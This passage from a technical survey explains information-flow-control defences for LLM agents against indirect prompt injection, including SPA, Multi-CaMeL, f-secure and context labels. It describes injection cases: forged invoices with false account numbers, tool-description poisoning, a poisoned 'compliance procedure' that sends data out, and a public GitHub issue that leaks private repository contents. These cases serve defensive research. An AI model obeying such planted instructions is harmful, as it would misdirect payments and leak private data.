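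Better reasoning can improve a planner's guesses about menus and error messages, but it can't supply a sequence of actions that exists only in an unread file. Foerster and colleagues accept this as a fundamental limit of keeping the planner away from the data. How much the limit matters depends on how often people set such tasks, which neither AgentDojo nor AgentDyn measures. Replanning is needed for 6 percent of tasks in AgentDojo and 100 percent in AgentDyn because the benchmarks' designers chose different tasks. Ma and colleagues expect typical users to leave details to the agent, but many of those requests will leave open only an amount or an address, which a single program can look up as it runs.

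## Planning again without showing the planner any data

An agent could get past some of these limits if the planner wrote a second program after the first had run, but text read by the first program could then influence the second. In a cautious design, the planner's prompt lists each earlier result by type but omits its contents.

Girrens and Wang built SPA on this principle for persistent agents, which keep results from one user request and reuse them in later ones. The planner runs once per request, so over a week it may write dozens of programs. Labels have to last as long as the results do, so SPA saves each label with its result. *MemLineage* (2026), a paper on agent memory, points out that FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues, erases its labels when a planner run ends. A result saved on Monday and reused on Tuesday would then have no record of its source.

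### A language with six kinds of step

SPA's planner writes in a small special-purpose language instead of Python. A plan is a list of steps in JSON, a common text format for structured data, and there are six kinds of step:

| Step | Effect |
|---|---|
| `retrieve` | loads a saved result into a variable |
| `tool` | calls an external tool, the only step that can act on the outside world |
| `q-llm` | gives data to the quarantined model and gets back an answer in a fixed format |
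| `display` | shows text or values to the user |
| `condition` | makes one comparison and runs one of two branches |
| `loop` | repeats some steps for each item in a collection |

The planner also writes two notes for every `tool` and `q-llm` step, one on the step's purpose and one on what its result will represent.

The language is deliberately restricted. A step can name a variable, select one of its fields or state a constant, but it can't do arithmetic or insert values into a text template. Combining two conditions with "and" requires nesting one inside the other. A branch can't overwrite variables defined outside it, and the variables it creates disappear when it ends. A checker can therefore find every dependency by reading the plan, without running it. The restrictions also avoid the gap that Garby and colleagues credit to Fenton, because skipping a branch can't leave an old value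 in a variable that later steps read.

### Checking the plan before it runs

SPA gives each value a confidentiality label $C$ and an integrity label $I$. It puts trusted data at the top of the integrity order, so combining labels means taking the higher confidentiality and the lower integrity. This is the same worst-input rule as before, with the integrity scale turned over. Data may flow from a source $s$ to a destination $d$ only if

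$$C(s) \sqsubseteq C(d) \quad\text{and}\quad I(d) \sqsubseteq I(s).$$

The destination must be cleared for data as secret as the source's, and the source must be at least as trusted as the destination requires.

For a tool call, the checker first combines the labels of everything the call depends on:

$$\lambda_{\text{eff}} = pc \sqcup \lambda(x_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \lambda(x_n)$$

Here $x_1, \dots, x_n$ are the variables in the arguments and $pc$ is the program-counter label. The checker then applies the flow rule with the tool as the destination. If the call passes, its result gets the label $\lambda_{\text{eff}} \sqcup \lambda_{\text{out}}$, where $\lambda_{\text{out}}$ is a fixed label for that tool's output. A web search needs $\lambda_{\text{out}}$ because even a trusted query brings back untrusted pages. An answer from the quarantined model gets only $\lambda_{\text{eff}}$, so a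 summary of an untrusted email is untrusted too.

When the checker reaches a condition, it adds the comparison's label to $pc$ and examines both branches. A tool that requires trusted input therefore can't run inside a branch whose condition depends on an untrusted email. This is stricter than control-flow integrity, which allows untrusted data to influence which branch runs.

If any tool call breaks the rule, SPA ends the request before running any step. If a `display` item is forbidden, SPA instead blanks it out and continues. Because SPA checks in advance, it would reject the bank-balance email plan whatever the balance was, whereas CaMeL's block on that email reveals that the balance is above the threshold. However, SPA also rejects a whole plan if it contains one forbidden call in a branch that would never have run.

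### An invoice on Monday and a payment on Tuesday

Girrens and Wang illustrate the problem with an invoice from a company called Acme. On Monday, a user asks the agent to find the invoice and keep its details. An attacker has added a false payment account to the invoice, along with an instruction aimed at any model that reads it. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday".

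Monday's plan might look like this in condensed form:

```
tool     search_email("Acme invoice")               -> mail
q-llm    "Extract the account and amount", mail      -> inv
display  "Saved the invoice. Amount due:", inv.amount
```

When the plan has finished, SPA saves both `mail` and `inv`. It splits each one into three parts, which for `inv` would be:

| Part | Contents | Used by |
|---|---|---|
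| Value | the false account number and the amount | the interpreter, while a plan runs |
| Label | private, untrusted | the checker |
| Description | two fields, `account` and `amount`; "payment details from the Acme invoice"; made for Monday's request | the planner |

The planted instruction is in the value of `mail`, which no planner will read. On Tuesday the planner receives the new request, a record of earlier ones and the descriptions. That is enough to pick out the right result and write:

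```
retrieve  inv                                        -> bill
tool      send_money(bill.account, bill.amount)      -> receipt
display   "Paid.", receipt
```

The `retrieve` step restores Monday's label, so the checker treats both arguments as untrusted. The policy for `send_money` requires trusted input, so SPA rejects the plan before any money moves. Hiding the value from the planner kept the planted instruction from working, but the payment to the false account would still have gone through without the saved label.

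The user's bill is still unpaid, and would be even if the invoice were genuine. SPA checks the plan before reading anything, so it has to label email by the tool that fetches it, and a message from the user's own accountant gets the same label as one from a stranger. The user could type the account number and the amount into a new request, since constants from the request carry the request's label. Typing only the account number would not be enough, because SPA sets a single integrity requirement for the whole call, and an amount taken from the invoice would make the call untrusted again.

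### Attack success, utility and reuse

AgentDojo resets the agent after every task, so it can't test what happens when a user makes another request in the same conversation. Girrens and Wang turned its 97 user tasks into conversations of two to five requests, called AgentDojo-MQ for "multi-query". For each task, they drew a graph by hand of the results it depends on, used a program to split the graph into turns, and had GPT-5.4 phrase the requests. In one task, the user first asks the agent to find a networking event in the calendar, then asks for the invitees' email addresses. The injections are in place from the start, and the benchmark scores the outcome after the last turn.

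A small model, GPT-5.4 nano, served as both planner and quarantined model. Each configuration went through the 97 tasks without attacks and 949 cases with them:

| Configuration | Attack success, AgentDojo | Attack success, AgentDojo-MQ | Utility, AgentDojo | Utility, AgentDojo-MQ | Reuse |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Flow check on | 0.0% | 0.2% | 29.0% | 35.3% | 89.9% |
| Flow check off | 0.4% | 0.3% | 53.0% | 62.5% | 95.4% |
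| Flow check off, planner sees saved values | – | 0.6% | – | 65.9% | 92.9% |

The utility figures come from runs without attacks. Reuse is the share of turns in which the plan retrieved an earlier result it needed, counting only turns where the earlier request had saved one. Counting unsaved results as failures lowers reuse to 73.4 percent with the check on and 80.1 percent with it off. When the right result had been saved, descriptions alone were usually enough to find it.

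The 0.2 percent is two runs. AgentDojo recorded both as successful attacks although SPA had rejected the plan, so the real figure may well be zero. On the original AgentDojo, the check stopped four attacks that succeeded when it was off, all in the same banking task. With the check off, the quarantined model's answers carried the attacker's content into tool arguments, which led to three unauthorised transfers and a changed password.

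It is harder to tell how much SPA contributed in the other 945 cases, because the comparison includes no ordinary agent running the same model. Li and colleagues suspect that developers have trained many newer models on the standard attack templates. The attacks are also a poor test of saved state, because they weren't designed to stay in a store and take effect in a later conversation. Girrens and Wang say their results don't settle how SPA would do against attacks designed that way.

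The loss of utility is much clearer. On AgentDojo, about 81 percent of runs reached execution with the check off. With it on, 37 percent did, and the check stopped 53 percent, typically because the plan passed untrusted output from one tool to another that requires trusted input. Many legitimate tasks need such a flow, such as paying a bill described in a file, but SPA has no endorsement step to approve it. The planner can't easily avoid these flows, because SPA hides the labels from it as well as the values, and a rejected plan ends the request. Girrens and Wang suggest labels for individual fields, separate requirements for each argument, and narrow forms of endorsement.

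Hiding the saved values from the planner reduced utility far less. Showing them raised utility by 3.4 points overall, but the effect varied widely across the benchmark. Banking rose from 56 to 81 percent, while travel, with only 20 tasks, fell from 70 to 50 percent. AgentDojo tests this only mildly because so few of its tasks require a change of plan. Even when the planner could see saved values, they came only from earlier requests, never from the plan in progress.

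Utility was higher on AgentDojo-MQ than on the original AgentDojo, but this doesn't show that memory helps, because the user in the multi-query version has already divided the task into steps, which is part of the planner's job.

### When one agent instructs another

A multi-agent system also calls planners repeatedly, even for a single user request. Each agent has its own planner, which writes a program when another agent sends it a request. By then, other agents may have read untrusted data. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' job-applicant example, text that one agent had correctly treated as untrusted became part of another agent's trusted instructions, a failure they call *boundary laundering*.

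They argue that protecting agents one at a time can't rule this out. In any system of two or more agents where some tool returns untrusted data and an agent can use one tool's result in its request to another agent, some user request will lead a planner to read untrusted text. The flaw is in the connection between the agents, and it exists even if each agent has control-flow integrity.

The proposed remedy, Multi-CaMeL, divides each message into an instruction, which the receiving planner reads, and variables, which it doesn't. The interpreter also carries the variables' labels across to the second agent. This split is similar to SPA's, with the instruction serving the same purpose as SPA's description.

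In one successful test run, a user asks which sensors on an industrial cooling unit, Chiller 6, could help detect an overheating compressor. The coordinating agent's program gets the list of sensors from one agent and stores it in a variable called `available_sensors`. It then sends a second agent a request to pick out the relevant ones, referring to the variable by name. The second planner isn't told whether the variable will hold a list or text, so its program handles both and tries again if the formatting is wrong. The agents identify 10 of the 12 sensors as potentially relevant.

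Multi-CaMeL's perfect score against attacks comes from MultiAgentDojo, which shares out AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialist agents and a coordinator. The same benchmark shows what the protection costs in completed tasks:

| Model | Attack success without CaMeL | Utility without CaMeL | Utility with CaMeL on each agent | Utility with Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 91.1% | 84.4% | 84.4% |
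| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 76.3% | 42.3% | 26.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 27.8% | 13.4% | 7.2% |

Fable 5 refused 52 of the 97 tasks, perhaps because they resembled a security test, so its utility figures cover only the other 45. GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro gained the most protection and lost about 50 points of utility. GPT-5.5 lost about 20 points and gained no measurable protection, since it had already resisted all 949 attacks unaided. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that attackers who adapt to a model do succeed, as they did against every frontier model tested in a large public red-teaming competition.

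Most of the loss in utility comes from CaMeL itself. On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks that includes the chiller question, putting CaMeL on each agent cut utility by an average of 21.6 points, and dividing the messages cut it by another 3.2. For the two strongest models, the first loss was 13.4 points and the second was 0.85.

The tests ran without data-flow policies, so they measure whether injections can add new actions but not whether they can supply false account numbers. Multi-CaMeL also inherits CaMeL's incomplete tracking of implicit flows, so the interpreter could label a message as trusted even when its wording depends on an untrusted condition.

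### Planning one step at a time

*System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) introduced f-secure, an earlier, related system that calls its planner much more often than SPA or Multi-CaMeL. It gets one step from the planner, runs it, and then requests the next. An untrusted result appears in the planner's prompt only as a reference such as `{Data_output:1}`. The planner can tell a later step to use that reference but can't read the data it points to. Trusted results, however, do go into the prompt.

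That makes real replanning possible when the useful data is trusted. In one of the paper's examples, a user wants the agent to read emails about budgets and notify a manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. The search finds two messages from colleagues, with budgets of $724 and $1,024, and one from an attacker. Because f-secure labels each email by its sender after fetching it, the planner receives the colleagues' budgets but not the attacker's email, and can decide to notify the manager. SPA could not make this distinction because its check comes before the search.

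Wu and colleagues prove a property they call execution trace non-compromise. Let $Q_1$ and $Q_2$ be two versions of all the information the system can reach, with identical trusted parts. For a request $q$ and any sequence of steps $\pi$,

$$\Pr[\pi \mid q, Q_1] = \Pr[\pi \mid q, Q_2].$$

Changing untrusted data can't make any sequence of steps more or less likely. On InjecAgent, a benchmark of planted instructions, no attack succeeded against f-secure with any of four models. Against an ordinary agent using GPT-4 Turbo, 29 to 45 percent of attacks succeeded, depending on the wording. F-secure completed tasks about as well as the ordinary agent, but Wu and colleagues measured this on separate benchmarks, so the results don't show how many tasks f-secure can finish while withholding data.

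Wu and colleagues' proof excludes attacks that make a tool unavailable, and its equation would not hold without that exclusion. When a step fails, f-secure requests another from the planner and keeps only the steps that worked. Suppose the planner is equally likely to pick either of two file readers, and an attacker's file crashes the first. Every completed sequence will then use the second reader, although the planner never received the file.

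Another difference Girrens and Wang note is that f-secure doesn't check the integrity of every tool's arguments. With the Acme invoice, f-secure's planner would never see the planted instruction, but a payment step could still send the money to the false account.

### What the planner can't do without the data

SPA's planner wrote the notes in the descriptions before the first plan ran, so they contain nothing about that plan's results. Almost everything new in the second program has to come from the user's second request. In effect, SPA produces a series of single-shot plans, and the user reads the results and decides what to do next.

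For the failed software build, SPA's first plan could show the end of the log to the user. The user could read the error and ask for a specific change to a file, which the planner could then write. This works when someone is there to read the log. An agent left to fix the build overnight would have only a description such as "last 50 lines of the build log", which is the same for every error. A repair written by the quarantined model would be untrusted, and a policy that protects the source files would reject it.

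A planner may also make up content about data it hasn't seen. One MultiAgentDojo task asks the agent to visit two people's websites and send them feedback. With Multi-CaMeL in place, Gemini 2.5 Pro's planner wrote the feedback into the program before the program had fetched either site. The feedback praised Dora's site for its clean design and informative content, but her page contained only a sentence saying whose it was, an email address and the planted instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues present the run as a completed task in which the defence worked. The defence did keep the run secure, but the planner had no way to detect that its praise was wrong. The protocol would have allowed the program to have the quarantined model write the feedback from the page instead.

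Descriptions can be wrong in the same way, because they record what the planner expected to get. In several AssetOpsBench runs, an agent could not find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something similar. The coordinating program, already written, used that data as if it were correct. SPA could make the same mistake a day later if Monday's search had returned last year's Acme invoice, because the description would still fit Tuesday's request.

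### Influence through the descriptions

The words of an invoice can't get into SPA's description of it, since the planner writes the description first. Other routes remain open.

One is the list of tools. In its normal mode, SPA shows the planner every installed tool's name, description and data format, and tool poisoning works through that text. *Think Twice Before You Act* (2026) describes attacks in which a tool's description adds harmful actions to the plan even though the planner never selects that tool. A persistent store could make this worse, because a planner that has read a poisoned description might repeat part of it in its notes. SPA would then show those notes to later planners as trusted text, even after someone had removed the tool.

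SPA has an optional mode that blocks this route. A model invents the tools that the request seems to need, the planner writes its plan using those tools, and a separate stage matches each one to an installed tool. The matching failed in about three quarters of runs. Utility on AgentDojo was 14.1 percent with the flow check off and 6.7 percent with it on, so for now the mode is too unreliable for most practical use.

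The presence or absence of a description can carry information too. SPA saves results only after a plan succeeds. If an attacker's malformed invoice makes Monday's plan fail, Tuesday's planner will find no saved invoice and will probably write a different program, perhaps one that searches the mailbox again. The attacker has then influenced that program without getting any text into it, and the flow rule doesn't label that influence. The channel carries only about one bit per request, and because SPA never retries on its own, an attacker can't use it faster than the user sends requests.

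The user can also copy text from an earlier output into a new request. SPA treats everything in a request as trusted, including an account number copied from Monday's output. This is a sensible endorsement if the user has checked the number, but SPA has no way to detect whether the user checked it or only pasted it.

More detailed descriptions would help the planner, but a note identifying the error in the build log, for example, could only come from reading the log. Under the flow rule, that note would be as untrusted as the log itself.

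## Writing new code after seeing results

The alternative is to let the planner read the log, find out why the build failed and write the repair itself, and then to treat whatever it writes as no more trustworthy than the log. Ba, Li and Li (2026), in *CIBER*, describe such agents as running a "Think-Code-Execute-Observe" loop. They found that current defences mainly filter the user's input and neglect tool outputs and conversation history, where outside text enters the loop.

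Labels are harder to assign here because the program's constants, branches and tool calls may come from the log instead of the user's request.

### Paying an invoice in three rounds

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the June invoice from Harlow Plumbing. The agent has three tools. `list_invoices` returns entries that the user's accounting software created, which the user trusts. `get_invoice` returns the text of an invoice as it arrived, which is untrusted. `send_money` makes a payment. Its policy requires a trusted account number but accepts an untrusted amount up to £2,000, because people often pay bills without knowing the exact total in advance.

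In the first round, the planner has read only the request, and it writes:

```
print(list_invoices("Harlow Plumbing"))
```

The output shows that invoice 412 arrived in June. The planner reads this and writes a second program:

```
print(get_invoice(412))
```

This prints the invoice:

```
HARLOW PLUMBING
Total:   GBP 1.240,00
Pay to:  70938214
```

Harlow uses a dot to separate thousands and a comma before the pence. A parser written for the usual British format could fail on this total or read it as £1.24. Having seen the format, the planner writes a parser that suits it, and copies the account number from the printed text:

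```
text = get_invoice(412)
total = text.split("GBP")[1].split()[0]
amount = float(total.replace(".", "").replace(",", "."))
send_money("70938214", amount)
```

Now suppose that someone intercepted the invoice and replaced Harlow's account number with their own. The invoice contains no planted instruction, so a filter that looks for instructions would find nothing. Whether the money goes to the attacker depends on the label of `"70938214"`:

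| Item | Where it came from | Label if new code counts as trusted | Label with a context label |
|---|---|---|---|
| First program | the request | trusted | trusted |
| List of invoices | accounting software | trusted | trusted |
| Second program, including `412` | the request and the list | trusted | trusted |
| Printed invoice | whoever wrote the invoice | untrusted | untrusted |
| `text`, `total` and `amount` | the invoice, through variables | untrusted | untrusted |
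| Parsing rules in the third program | the planner, after reading the invoice | trusted | untrusted |
| `"70938214"` | the invoice, through the planner | trusted | untrusted |
| Decision to call `send_money` | the planner, after reading the invoice | trusted | untrusted |
| **Payment** | | **allowed** | **blocked** |

### How the constant loses its label

A tracker that trusts new code labels `text` as untrusted because of the tool that returned it, and `amount` as untrusted because the program computed it from `text`. But it treats the account number, `"70938214"`, as trusted because it is a constant in the code, like the `0` in `split()[0]`. The invoice had a label when it entered the planner's prompt, but the planner wrote the account number into the program without that label.

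This tracker would have blocked a more careful program. If the planner had parsed the account number from `text`, the number would have been labeled untrusted and the policy would have rejected it. Retyping the number removes that label. An agent that received the rejection as an error might well retype the number on its next attempt, just because that is another way to write the program.

Trusting constants is reasonable in single-shot programs, where the rule began. *CaMeLoT* (2026), an extension that checks CaMeL's plans before they run, builds on the same division, in which values from the user are trusted and values from tools may not be. A constant in a single-shot program belongs with the user's values because the planner has read no tool output. Trusting constants stops being safe once the planner reads the invoice. A developer could still trust them by mistake just by calling a single-shot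 interpreter repeatedly, and CaMeL's own retry loop has the same flaw with error messages.

*Agent-Sentry* (2026) uses a safer default. It records whether each argument came from the user's prompt or from particular earlier tool calls, and treats the argument as adversarial if the recorded source doesn't match anything in the run. It would therefore treat the payment's account number as adversarial if the number's origin were unknown. Identifying the source of a value that a model has generated is harder, since an incorrect source would still pass if it matched something in the run.

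### One label for everything the planner has read

A context label avoids having to trace each constant. The system keeps one label for the conversation and joins it with the label of everything the planner reads. Let $c_0$ be the label of the user's request, and let $o_k$ be the label of the output that the planner receives from program $k$. Then

$$c_k = c_{k-1} \sqcup o_k,$$

and $c_k$ becomes the starting label for everything in program $k+1$. A constant in that program has the label $c_k$. A value computed from variables $x_1, \dots, x_n$ has the label

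$$c_k \sqcup \lambda(x_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \lambda(x_n).$$

In the invoice example, $c_0$ and $c_1$ are both trusted, because the planner has read only the request and the user's own records. The printed invoice makes $o_2$ untrusted, so $c_2$ is untrusted too. The account number in the third program inherits that label, and the policy blocks the payment.

Costa and colleagues apply this rule to agents that request tools directly. In their basic tracking planner, the tool name and every argument take the label of the whole conversation. A copied account number therefore has the same label as one the model made up. When an agent writes a program, the system also has to pass the label to the generated code. Garby and colleagues do this by running the code under the conversation's label.

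Only information that reaches the planner raises the context label. The third program reads the invoice again but keeps the text in a variable, so the read would not raise the label even if the conversation had been clean until then. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* (2026), a paper on attacks that spread from agent to agent, similarly distinguishes loading a file into a model's context, which contaminates the model, from an "opaque" read, which returns only something limited, such as a hash, an error code or whether the file is valid. Even these results can reveal a little about the file, so a strict tracker would label them too.

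As with SPA and the Acme invoice, the payment would fail even with a genuine account number, unless the user typed the number into the request.

### Influence without copied text

An easier remedy would be to keep trusting new code but search it for strings the planner has just read. This would catch the account number in the invoice example, but not if the planner split it into two constants or joined it to a sort code in a different format. It would also produce false alarms, since a constant such as `30` could match a due date by coincidence.

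Text is even harder to match after a model rewrites it. Cai and colleagues describe a research agent that reads a web page containing a hidden instruction to rewrite a confidential patient note in "polished analyst language" and include it in its memo. The agent complies, and the memo contains no exact string from the planted text. They therefore count a flow as explicit if the original content is still recognisable after rewriting.

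The planner's choice of tool can be an implicit flow. In another of their test cases, an agent normally searches the web and passes the results to a tool that executes code. A poisoned search result describes a new compliance procedure that requires the agent to first submit its results to an outside address. The agent then calls a tool that sends the research to the attacker, instead of calling the tool that executes code. Cai and colleagues say that such an attack leaves no data footprint, although in this case the attacker's address does appear in the call, so a string search would find it. An invoice could change the choice of tool without supplying any argument. If it listed the payment as due every month, the planner might create a standing order instead of a single payment, using the account number and amount that the user had provided.

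The structure of the program can also depend on what the planner has read. Suppose the invoice includes a note that Harlow has recently changed banks and that some customers will see two account numbers. The planner might add a branch that prefers the new number whenever both appear. A program-counter label would record that the condition depends on the invoice's text, but not that the branch exists only because the planner read the note. Peters-Gill and colleagues permit untrusted data to select among branches because the plan fixes them all in advance. That reasoning no longer applies when the data can influence which branches the planner writes.

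Omissions are the most difficult case for a tracker that labels individual values, because missing code has no value to label. Suppose the planner would normally compare the account number with the one in the user's records before paying. The invoice contains a statement that the accounts department has already verified the new details, so the planner leaves out the comparison. The resulting program has no suspicious constant or extra branch.

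Similar omissions can occur without an attacker. *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (2026) examines whether reading insecure code leads an agent to write insecure code. The researchers give an agent the same task in versions of a repository that differ only in whether related code is secure, so a change in the security of the agent's code can be attributed to what it read. For example, if the existing functions don't check their input, an agent might follow their style and leave the check out of a new function. A string search would find little evidence of this influence, because the check is missing from both the old code and the new.

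These influences can be strong. In *CARI*, Fu, Wu and colleagues (2026) put malicious instructions into feedback from running software, and coding agents carried them out in 2,845 of 3,000 trials.

A context label covers all four kinds of influence because it doesn't depend on identifying them. If the planner has read the forged invoice, every call in the next program is untrusted, including a payment that looks harmless because a check is missing. *Autonomous LLM Agent Worms* defends this caution. It argues that no general procedure can decide whether exposed content materially influenced a model's later decisions. Under its rule, everything a contaminated model writes is tainted, and the model can't remove the taint from its own output without a separate declassification procedure.

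Even so, a check at a sink can act only on calls the program makes. If the invoice contains the false statement "already paid by direct debit", the planner may skip the payment. A policy then has no payment to inspect, and Harlow goes unpaid. A context label can still show the user that the agent's final answer is untrusted, but it can't make the missing payment.

### The same idea in older software

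Researchers used a single label for a whole computation long before they applied it to language models. Buiras, Stefan and Russo (2015), in *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, describe a library called LIO for the programming language Haskell. LIO gives a running computation one "current" label, which covers everything in scope that doesn't have a label of its own. Reading data with label $l_d$ raises the current label:

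$$l'_{\text{cur}} = l_{\text{cur}} \sqcup l_d$$

After that, the computation may write only to a place whose label $l_e$ satisfies $l'_{\text{cur}} \sqsubseteq l_e$. For example, a computation that has read a secret can no longer write to a public file.

This makes implicit flows easy to handle. The condition of every `if` statement already has the current label, so a program cannot branch on a secret to control what it writes to a public file. A planner's context label works in much the same way. It applies to the whole generated program, as though the program were inside a branch whose condition depended on everything in the conversation.

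The drawback is also the same. Buiras and colleagues give the example of a program that reads a secret and then tries to write the number 42 to a public channel. LIO blocks the write even though the number has nothing to do with the secret. To avoid this, LIO also lets programmers wrap a value in its own label, so the program can carry the value around and raise the current label only when it reads the value.

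Fine-grained systems label each value separately, while coarse-grained systems label a whole computation. *From Fine- to Coarse-Grained Dynamic Information Flow Control and Back* (2022) describes coarse-grained systems as often easier to build, but more prone to label creep. It also proves that the two approaches are equally expressive, but the proof concerns programs in which a monitor can follow every step. A planner combines the request, the list of invoices and the invoice itself inside one model call, where a monitor outside the model has no separate steps to label. The result therefore doesn't show that an agent could use a simple context label without losing precision.

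*Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (2012), an earlier paper on LIO, adds the current clearance, a limit that a programmer sets in advance and that the current label may not rise above. An agent could use a similar limit to refuse any read that would taint its context until it has finished making payments. This works if the user has supplied the payment details and also wants a summary of the day's email, since the agent can make the payments before it reads the email. It doesn't help with Harlow's invoice, where the agent has to read the untrusted text to find out whom to pay.

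### How quickly labels spread

A context label never goes down by itself, because a join can only keep a label the same or make it more restrictive. One untrusted result is therefore enough to taint the rest of the conversation. If each round has a probability $p$ of adding untrusted data, independently of the others, the probability that the context is still trusted after $n$ rounds is

$$(1-p)^n.$$

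With a 20 percent chance per round, $0.8^{10} \approx 0.107$, so only about 11 percent of conversations are still clean after ten rounds. Half have lost their trusted label by about the third round. Reducing the chance per round helps, but long conversations remain a problem:

| Chance of untrusted data per round | Clean after 3 rounds | Clean after 5 | Clean after 10 | Clean after 20 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
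| 1% | 97% | 95% | 90% | 82% |
| 5% | 86% | 77% | 60% | 36% |
| 20% | 51% | 33% | 11% | 1% |

The 20 percent is only an illustration, and real rounds are not independent. If one conversation in five read untrusted data in every round and the rest never did, the average chance per round would still be 20 percent, but 80 percent of conversations would be clean after ten rounds. Label creep depends heavily on the kind of work. A web-research agent will probably taint its context with its first search, while an agent that works on a company's internal documents may never read anything untrusted. The table is most relevant to mixed work, such as coding with occasional web searches, where any round might bring in outside text.

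An agent with a tainted context can still read files, run calculations and answer questions, as long as the policies treat these as harmless. But it can no longer take actions that require trust, which often include the one that would complete the task. Trying again doesn't help, because the next program inherits the taint.

The context label even blocks some tasks that need no replanning. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if the same sequence of tool calls and the same final response would solve it regardless of the data. Their example is a request to read the top three emails and send them to a particular Slack user. The request determines both tools and the recipient, so a system that passes the emails through a variable can complete it with a fixed plan. A basic planner instead puts the emails into the conversation, then writes the Slack call. The call fails under a policy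 that permits a tool call only if the model generated it from trusted inputs. An attacker might have influenced the call, even though the user had already specified everything except the message text.

A new conversation would start with a clean label, but the new planner would know nothing about the earlier results, and any note from the old planner would be tainted too. To keep useful information without the taint, the system would need a way to endorse selected parts of that information.

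### The context label in GitHub Copilot CLI

Microsoft worked with GitHub to add an experimental context label to GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent. Developers turn it on by setting `FIDES_IFC=true` when they start the program. Copilot CLI then updates a single label after each tool result and attaches that label to each tool call. Before certain calls, it checks the label against a policy. If a call breaks the policy, Copilot CLI can show the developer a dialog before going ahead.

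The labels come from GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting agents to tools. The documentation for version 1.0.5 of the label package, pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), gives rules for common results:

| Tool result | Integrity | Confidentiality |
|---|---|---|
| File in a public repository | untrusted | public |
| File in a private repository | trusted | private |
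| Issues in a public repository | untrusted | public |
| Issues in a private repository | untrusted | private |
| Search across repositories | untrusted | private if any matching repository is private, otherwise public |

The rules for files reflect who can change them. Anyone may propose a change to a public repository, while only collaborators can add changes to a private one. This is a rough guide to trust, because if a collaborator pastes a customer's email into a private file, the customer's text is treated as trusted.

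Under these rules, a developer who asks about open issues immediately makes the context untrusted, even in a private repository. A search that finds nothing has the same effect, because the package labels an empty result as public and untrusted. An empty result can warrant this label because text written by an outsider can affect whether a search finds anything.

Microsoft illustrates the protection with an attack that researchers demonstrated against coding assistants connected to GitHub. An attacker opens an issue in a public repository, asking for information from a private repository to appear in a comment. The developer asks the agent to deal with the issue, and the agent can read both repositories. Reading the issue makes the context public and untrusted. Reading the private file then gives

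$$(\text{public}, U) \sqcup (\text{private}, T) = (\text{private}, U).$$

The policy forbids an agent with this context from posting to a public channel, so it blocks the comment. It would still block the comment if the agent had paraphrased the file or written the comment with a new script that called the same tool, because the label applies to the whole context.

This policy blocks fewer actions than one that requires trust for every consequential action. An agent that has read only public data can still post in a public repository, even after reading an attacker's issue. Microsoft says that work confined to only public or only private repositories can proceed without interruption. Because the policy mainly protects secrets, it wouldn't by itself prevent an injected issue from making the agent post a misleading public comment.

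Label creep is still possible when a task combines both kinds of repository. Suppose each round has a 20 percent chance of adding untrusted data and, independently, a 20 percent chance of adding private data. After ten rounds, about 80 percent of conversations will carry both labels, and the policy will stop the agent from posting publicly without review. Microsoft warns that asking people to approve actions scales poorly and makes them less vigilant, so a developer who sees the dialog in most long sessions may start approving requests without reading them.

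The sources also label private issues differently. Microsoft's article describes them as trusted, whereas the package documentation labels issue contents untrusted in every repository. If an agent has read only private issues, the rule above would let it post their contents publicly under the article's labels but not under the package's. Calling private issues trusted assumes that everyone who can write one is also entitled to influence what the agent makes public.

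So far, Copilot CLI applies its built-in policies only to selected tools from GitHub's MCP server. This gap is more serious for an agent that writes code, because a script can send data over the network without calling GitHub's comment tool. Even if the context label correctly marks the script as private and untrusted, the label has no effect unless the system checks it before the script sends anything.

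## A proof that covers agents which generate code

A context label protects a conversation only if the software applies it to every prompt, every constant in the new program and every branch. Missing one path can remove that protection, as happens in CaMeL's retry loop. To prevent this, Garby and colleagues build the label rules into a small programming language called LLMbda. They prove a security theorem about every program in that language, including programs that ask a model for code and run it. They wrote the language's definition, its interpreter and the proofs in Lean, which checks each step of a proof by computer.

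### Four operations on a conversation

LLMbda extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions and calls to them. It adds a conversation with a model, which a program can change through four operations:

| Operation | Effect |
|---|---|
| `send e` | works out the value of `e`, turns it into text and adds it to the conversation |
| `recv` | gets the model's next message, adds it to the conversation, reads it as code and runs that code |
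| `fork e` | runs `e` on a copy of the conversation, then goes back to the original and keeps only the result |
| `clear` | empties the conversation |

The shorthand `@e` means `send e` followed by `recv`. Every reply counts as code, but the code can be as simple as a number or a quoted string. If the reply isn't valid code, the program receives an error message that it can send back to the model.

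One of the paper's examples extracts postcodes from three addresses. The program explains the postcode format to the model once, then forks the conversation for each address, so each query starts with that explanation and includes only one address.

These operations are enough to write the agents described so far. A single-shot planner calls `@` once and runs the program it gets back. A multi-shot agent is a loop that sends each program's output to the model and runs the next reply.

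### Labels on conversations and on generated code

In the simplest version of LLMbda, a label is a set that may contain U for untrusted and S for secret. Data with an empty label is trusted and public. Each value has a label, and the conversation has a single label, $l_c$. The interpreter keeps a program-counter label, $pc$.

When a program sends a value with label $n$, the conversation's label becomes $l_c \sqcup n$. If the value is a record with several fields, $n$ includes the labels of all of them, so one untrusted field makes the whole message untrusted. When the program then calls `recv`, the interpreter runs the model's code with

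$$pc = l_c.$$

Everything the code computes has at least this label. In the Harlow Plumbing example, the account number in the third program therefore gets the label U. If `send_money` begins with an `assert` that its recipient is trusted, the program stops there.

This is the same context label, but the developer no longer has to remember to attach it to new code. The theorem also holds for any code the model returns, even if an attacker has complete control of the reply.

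### The branch that doesn't run

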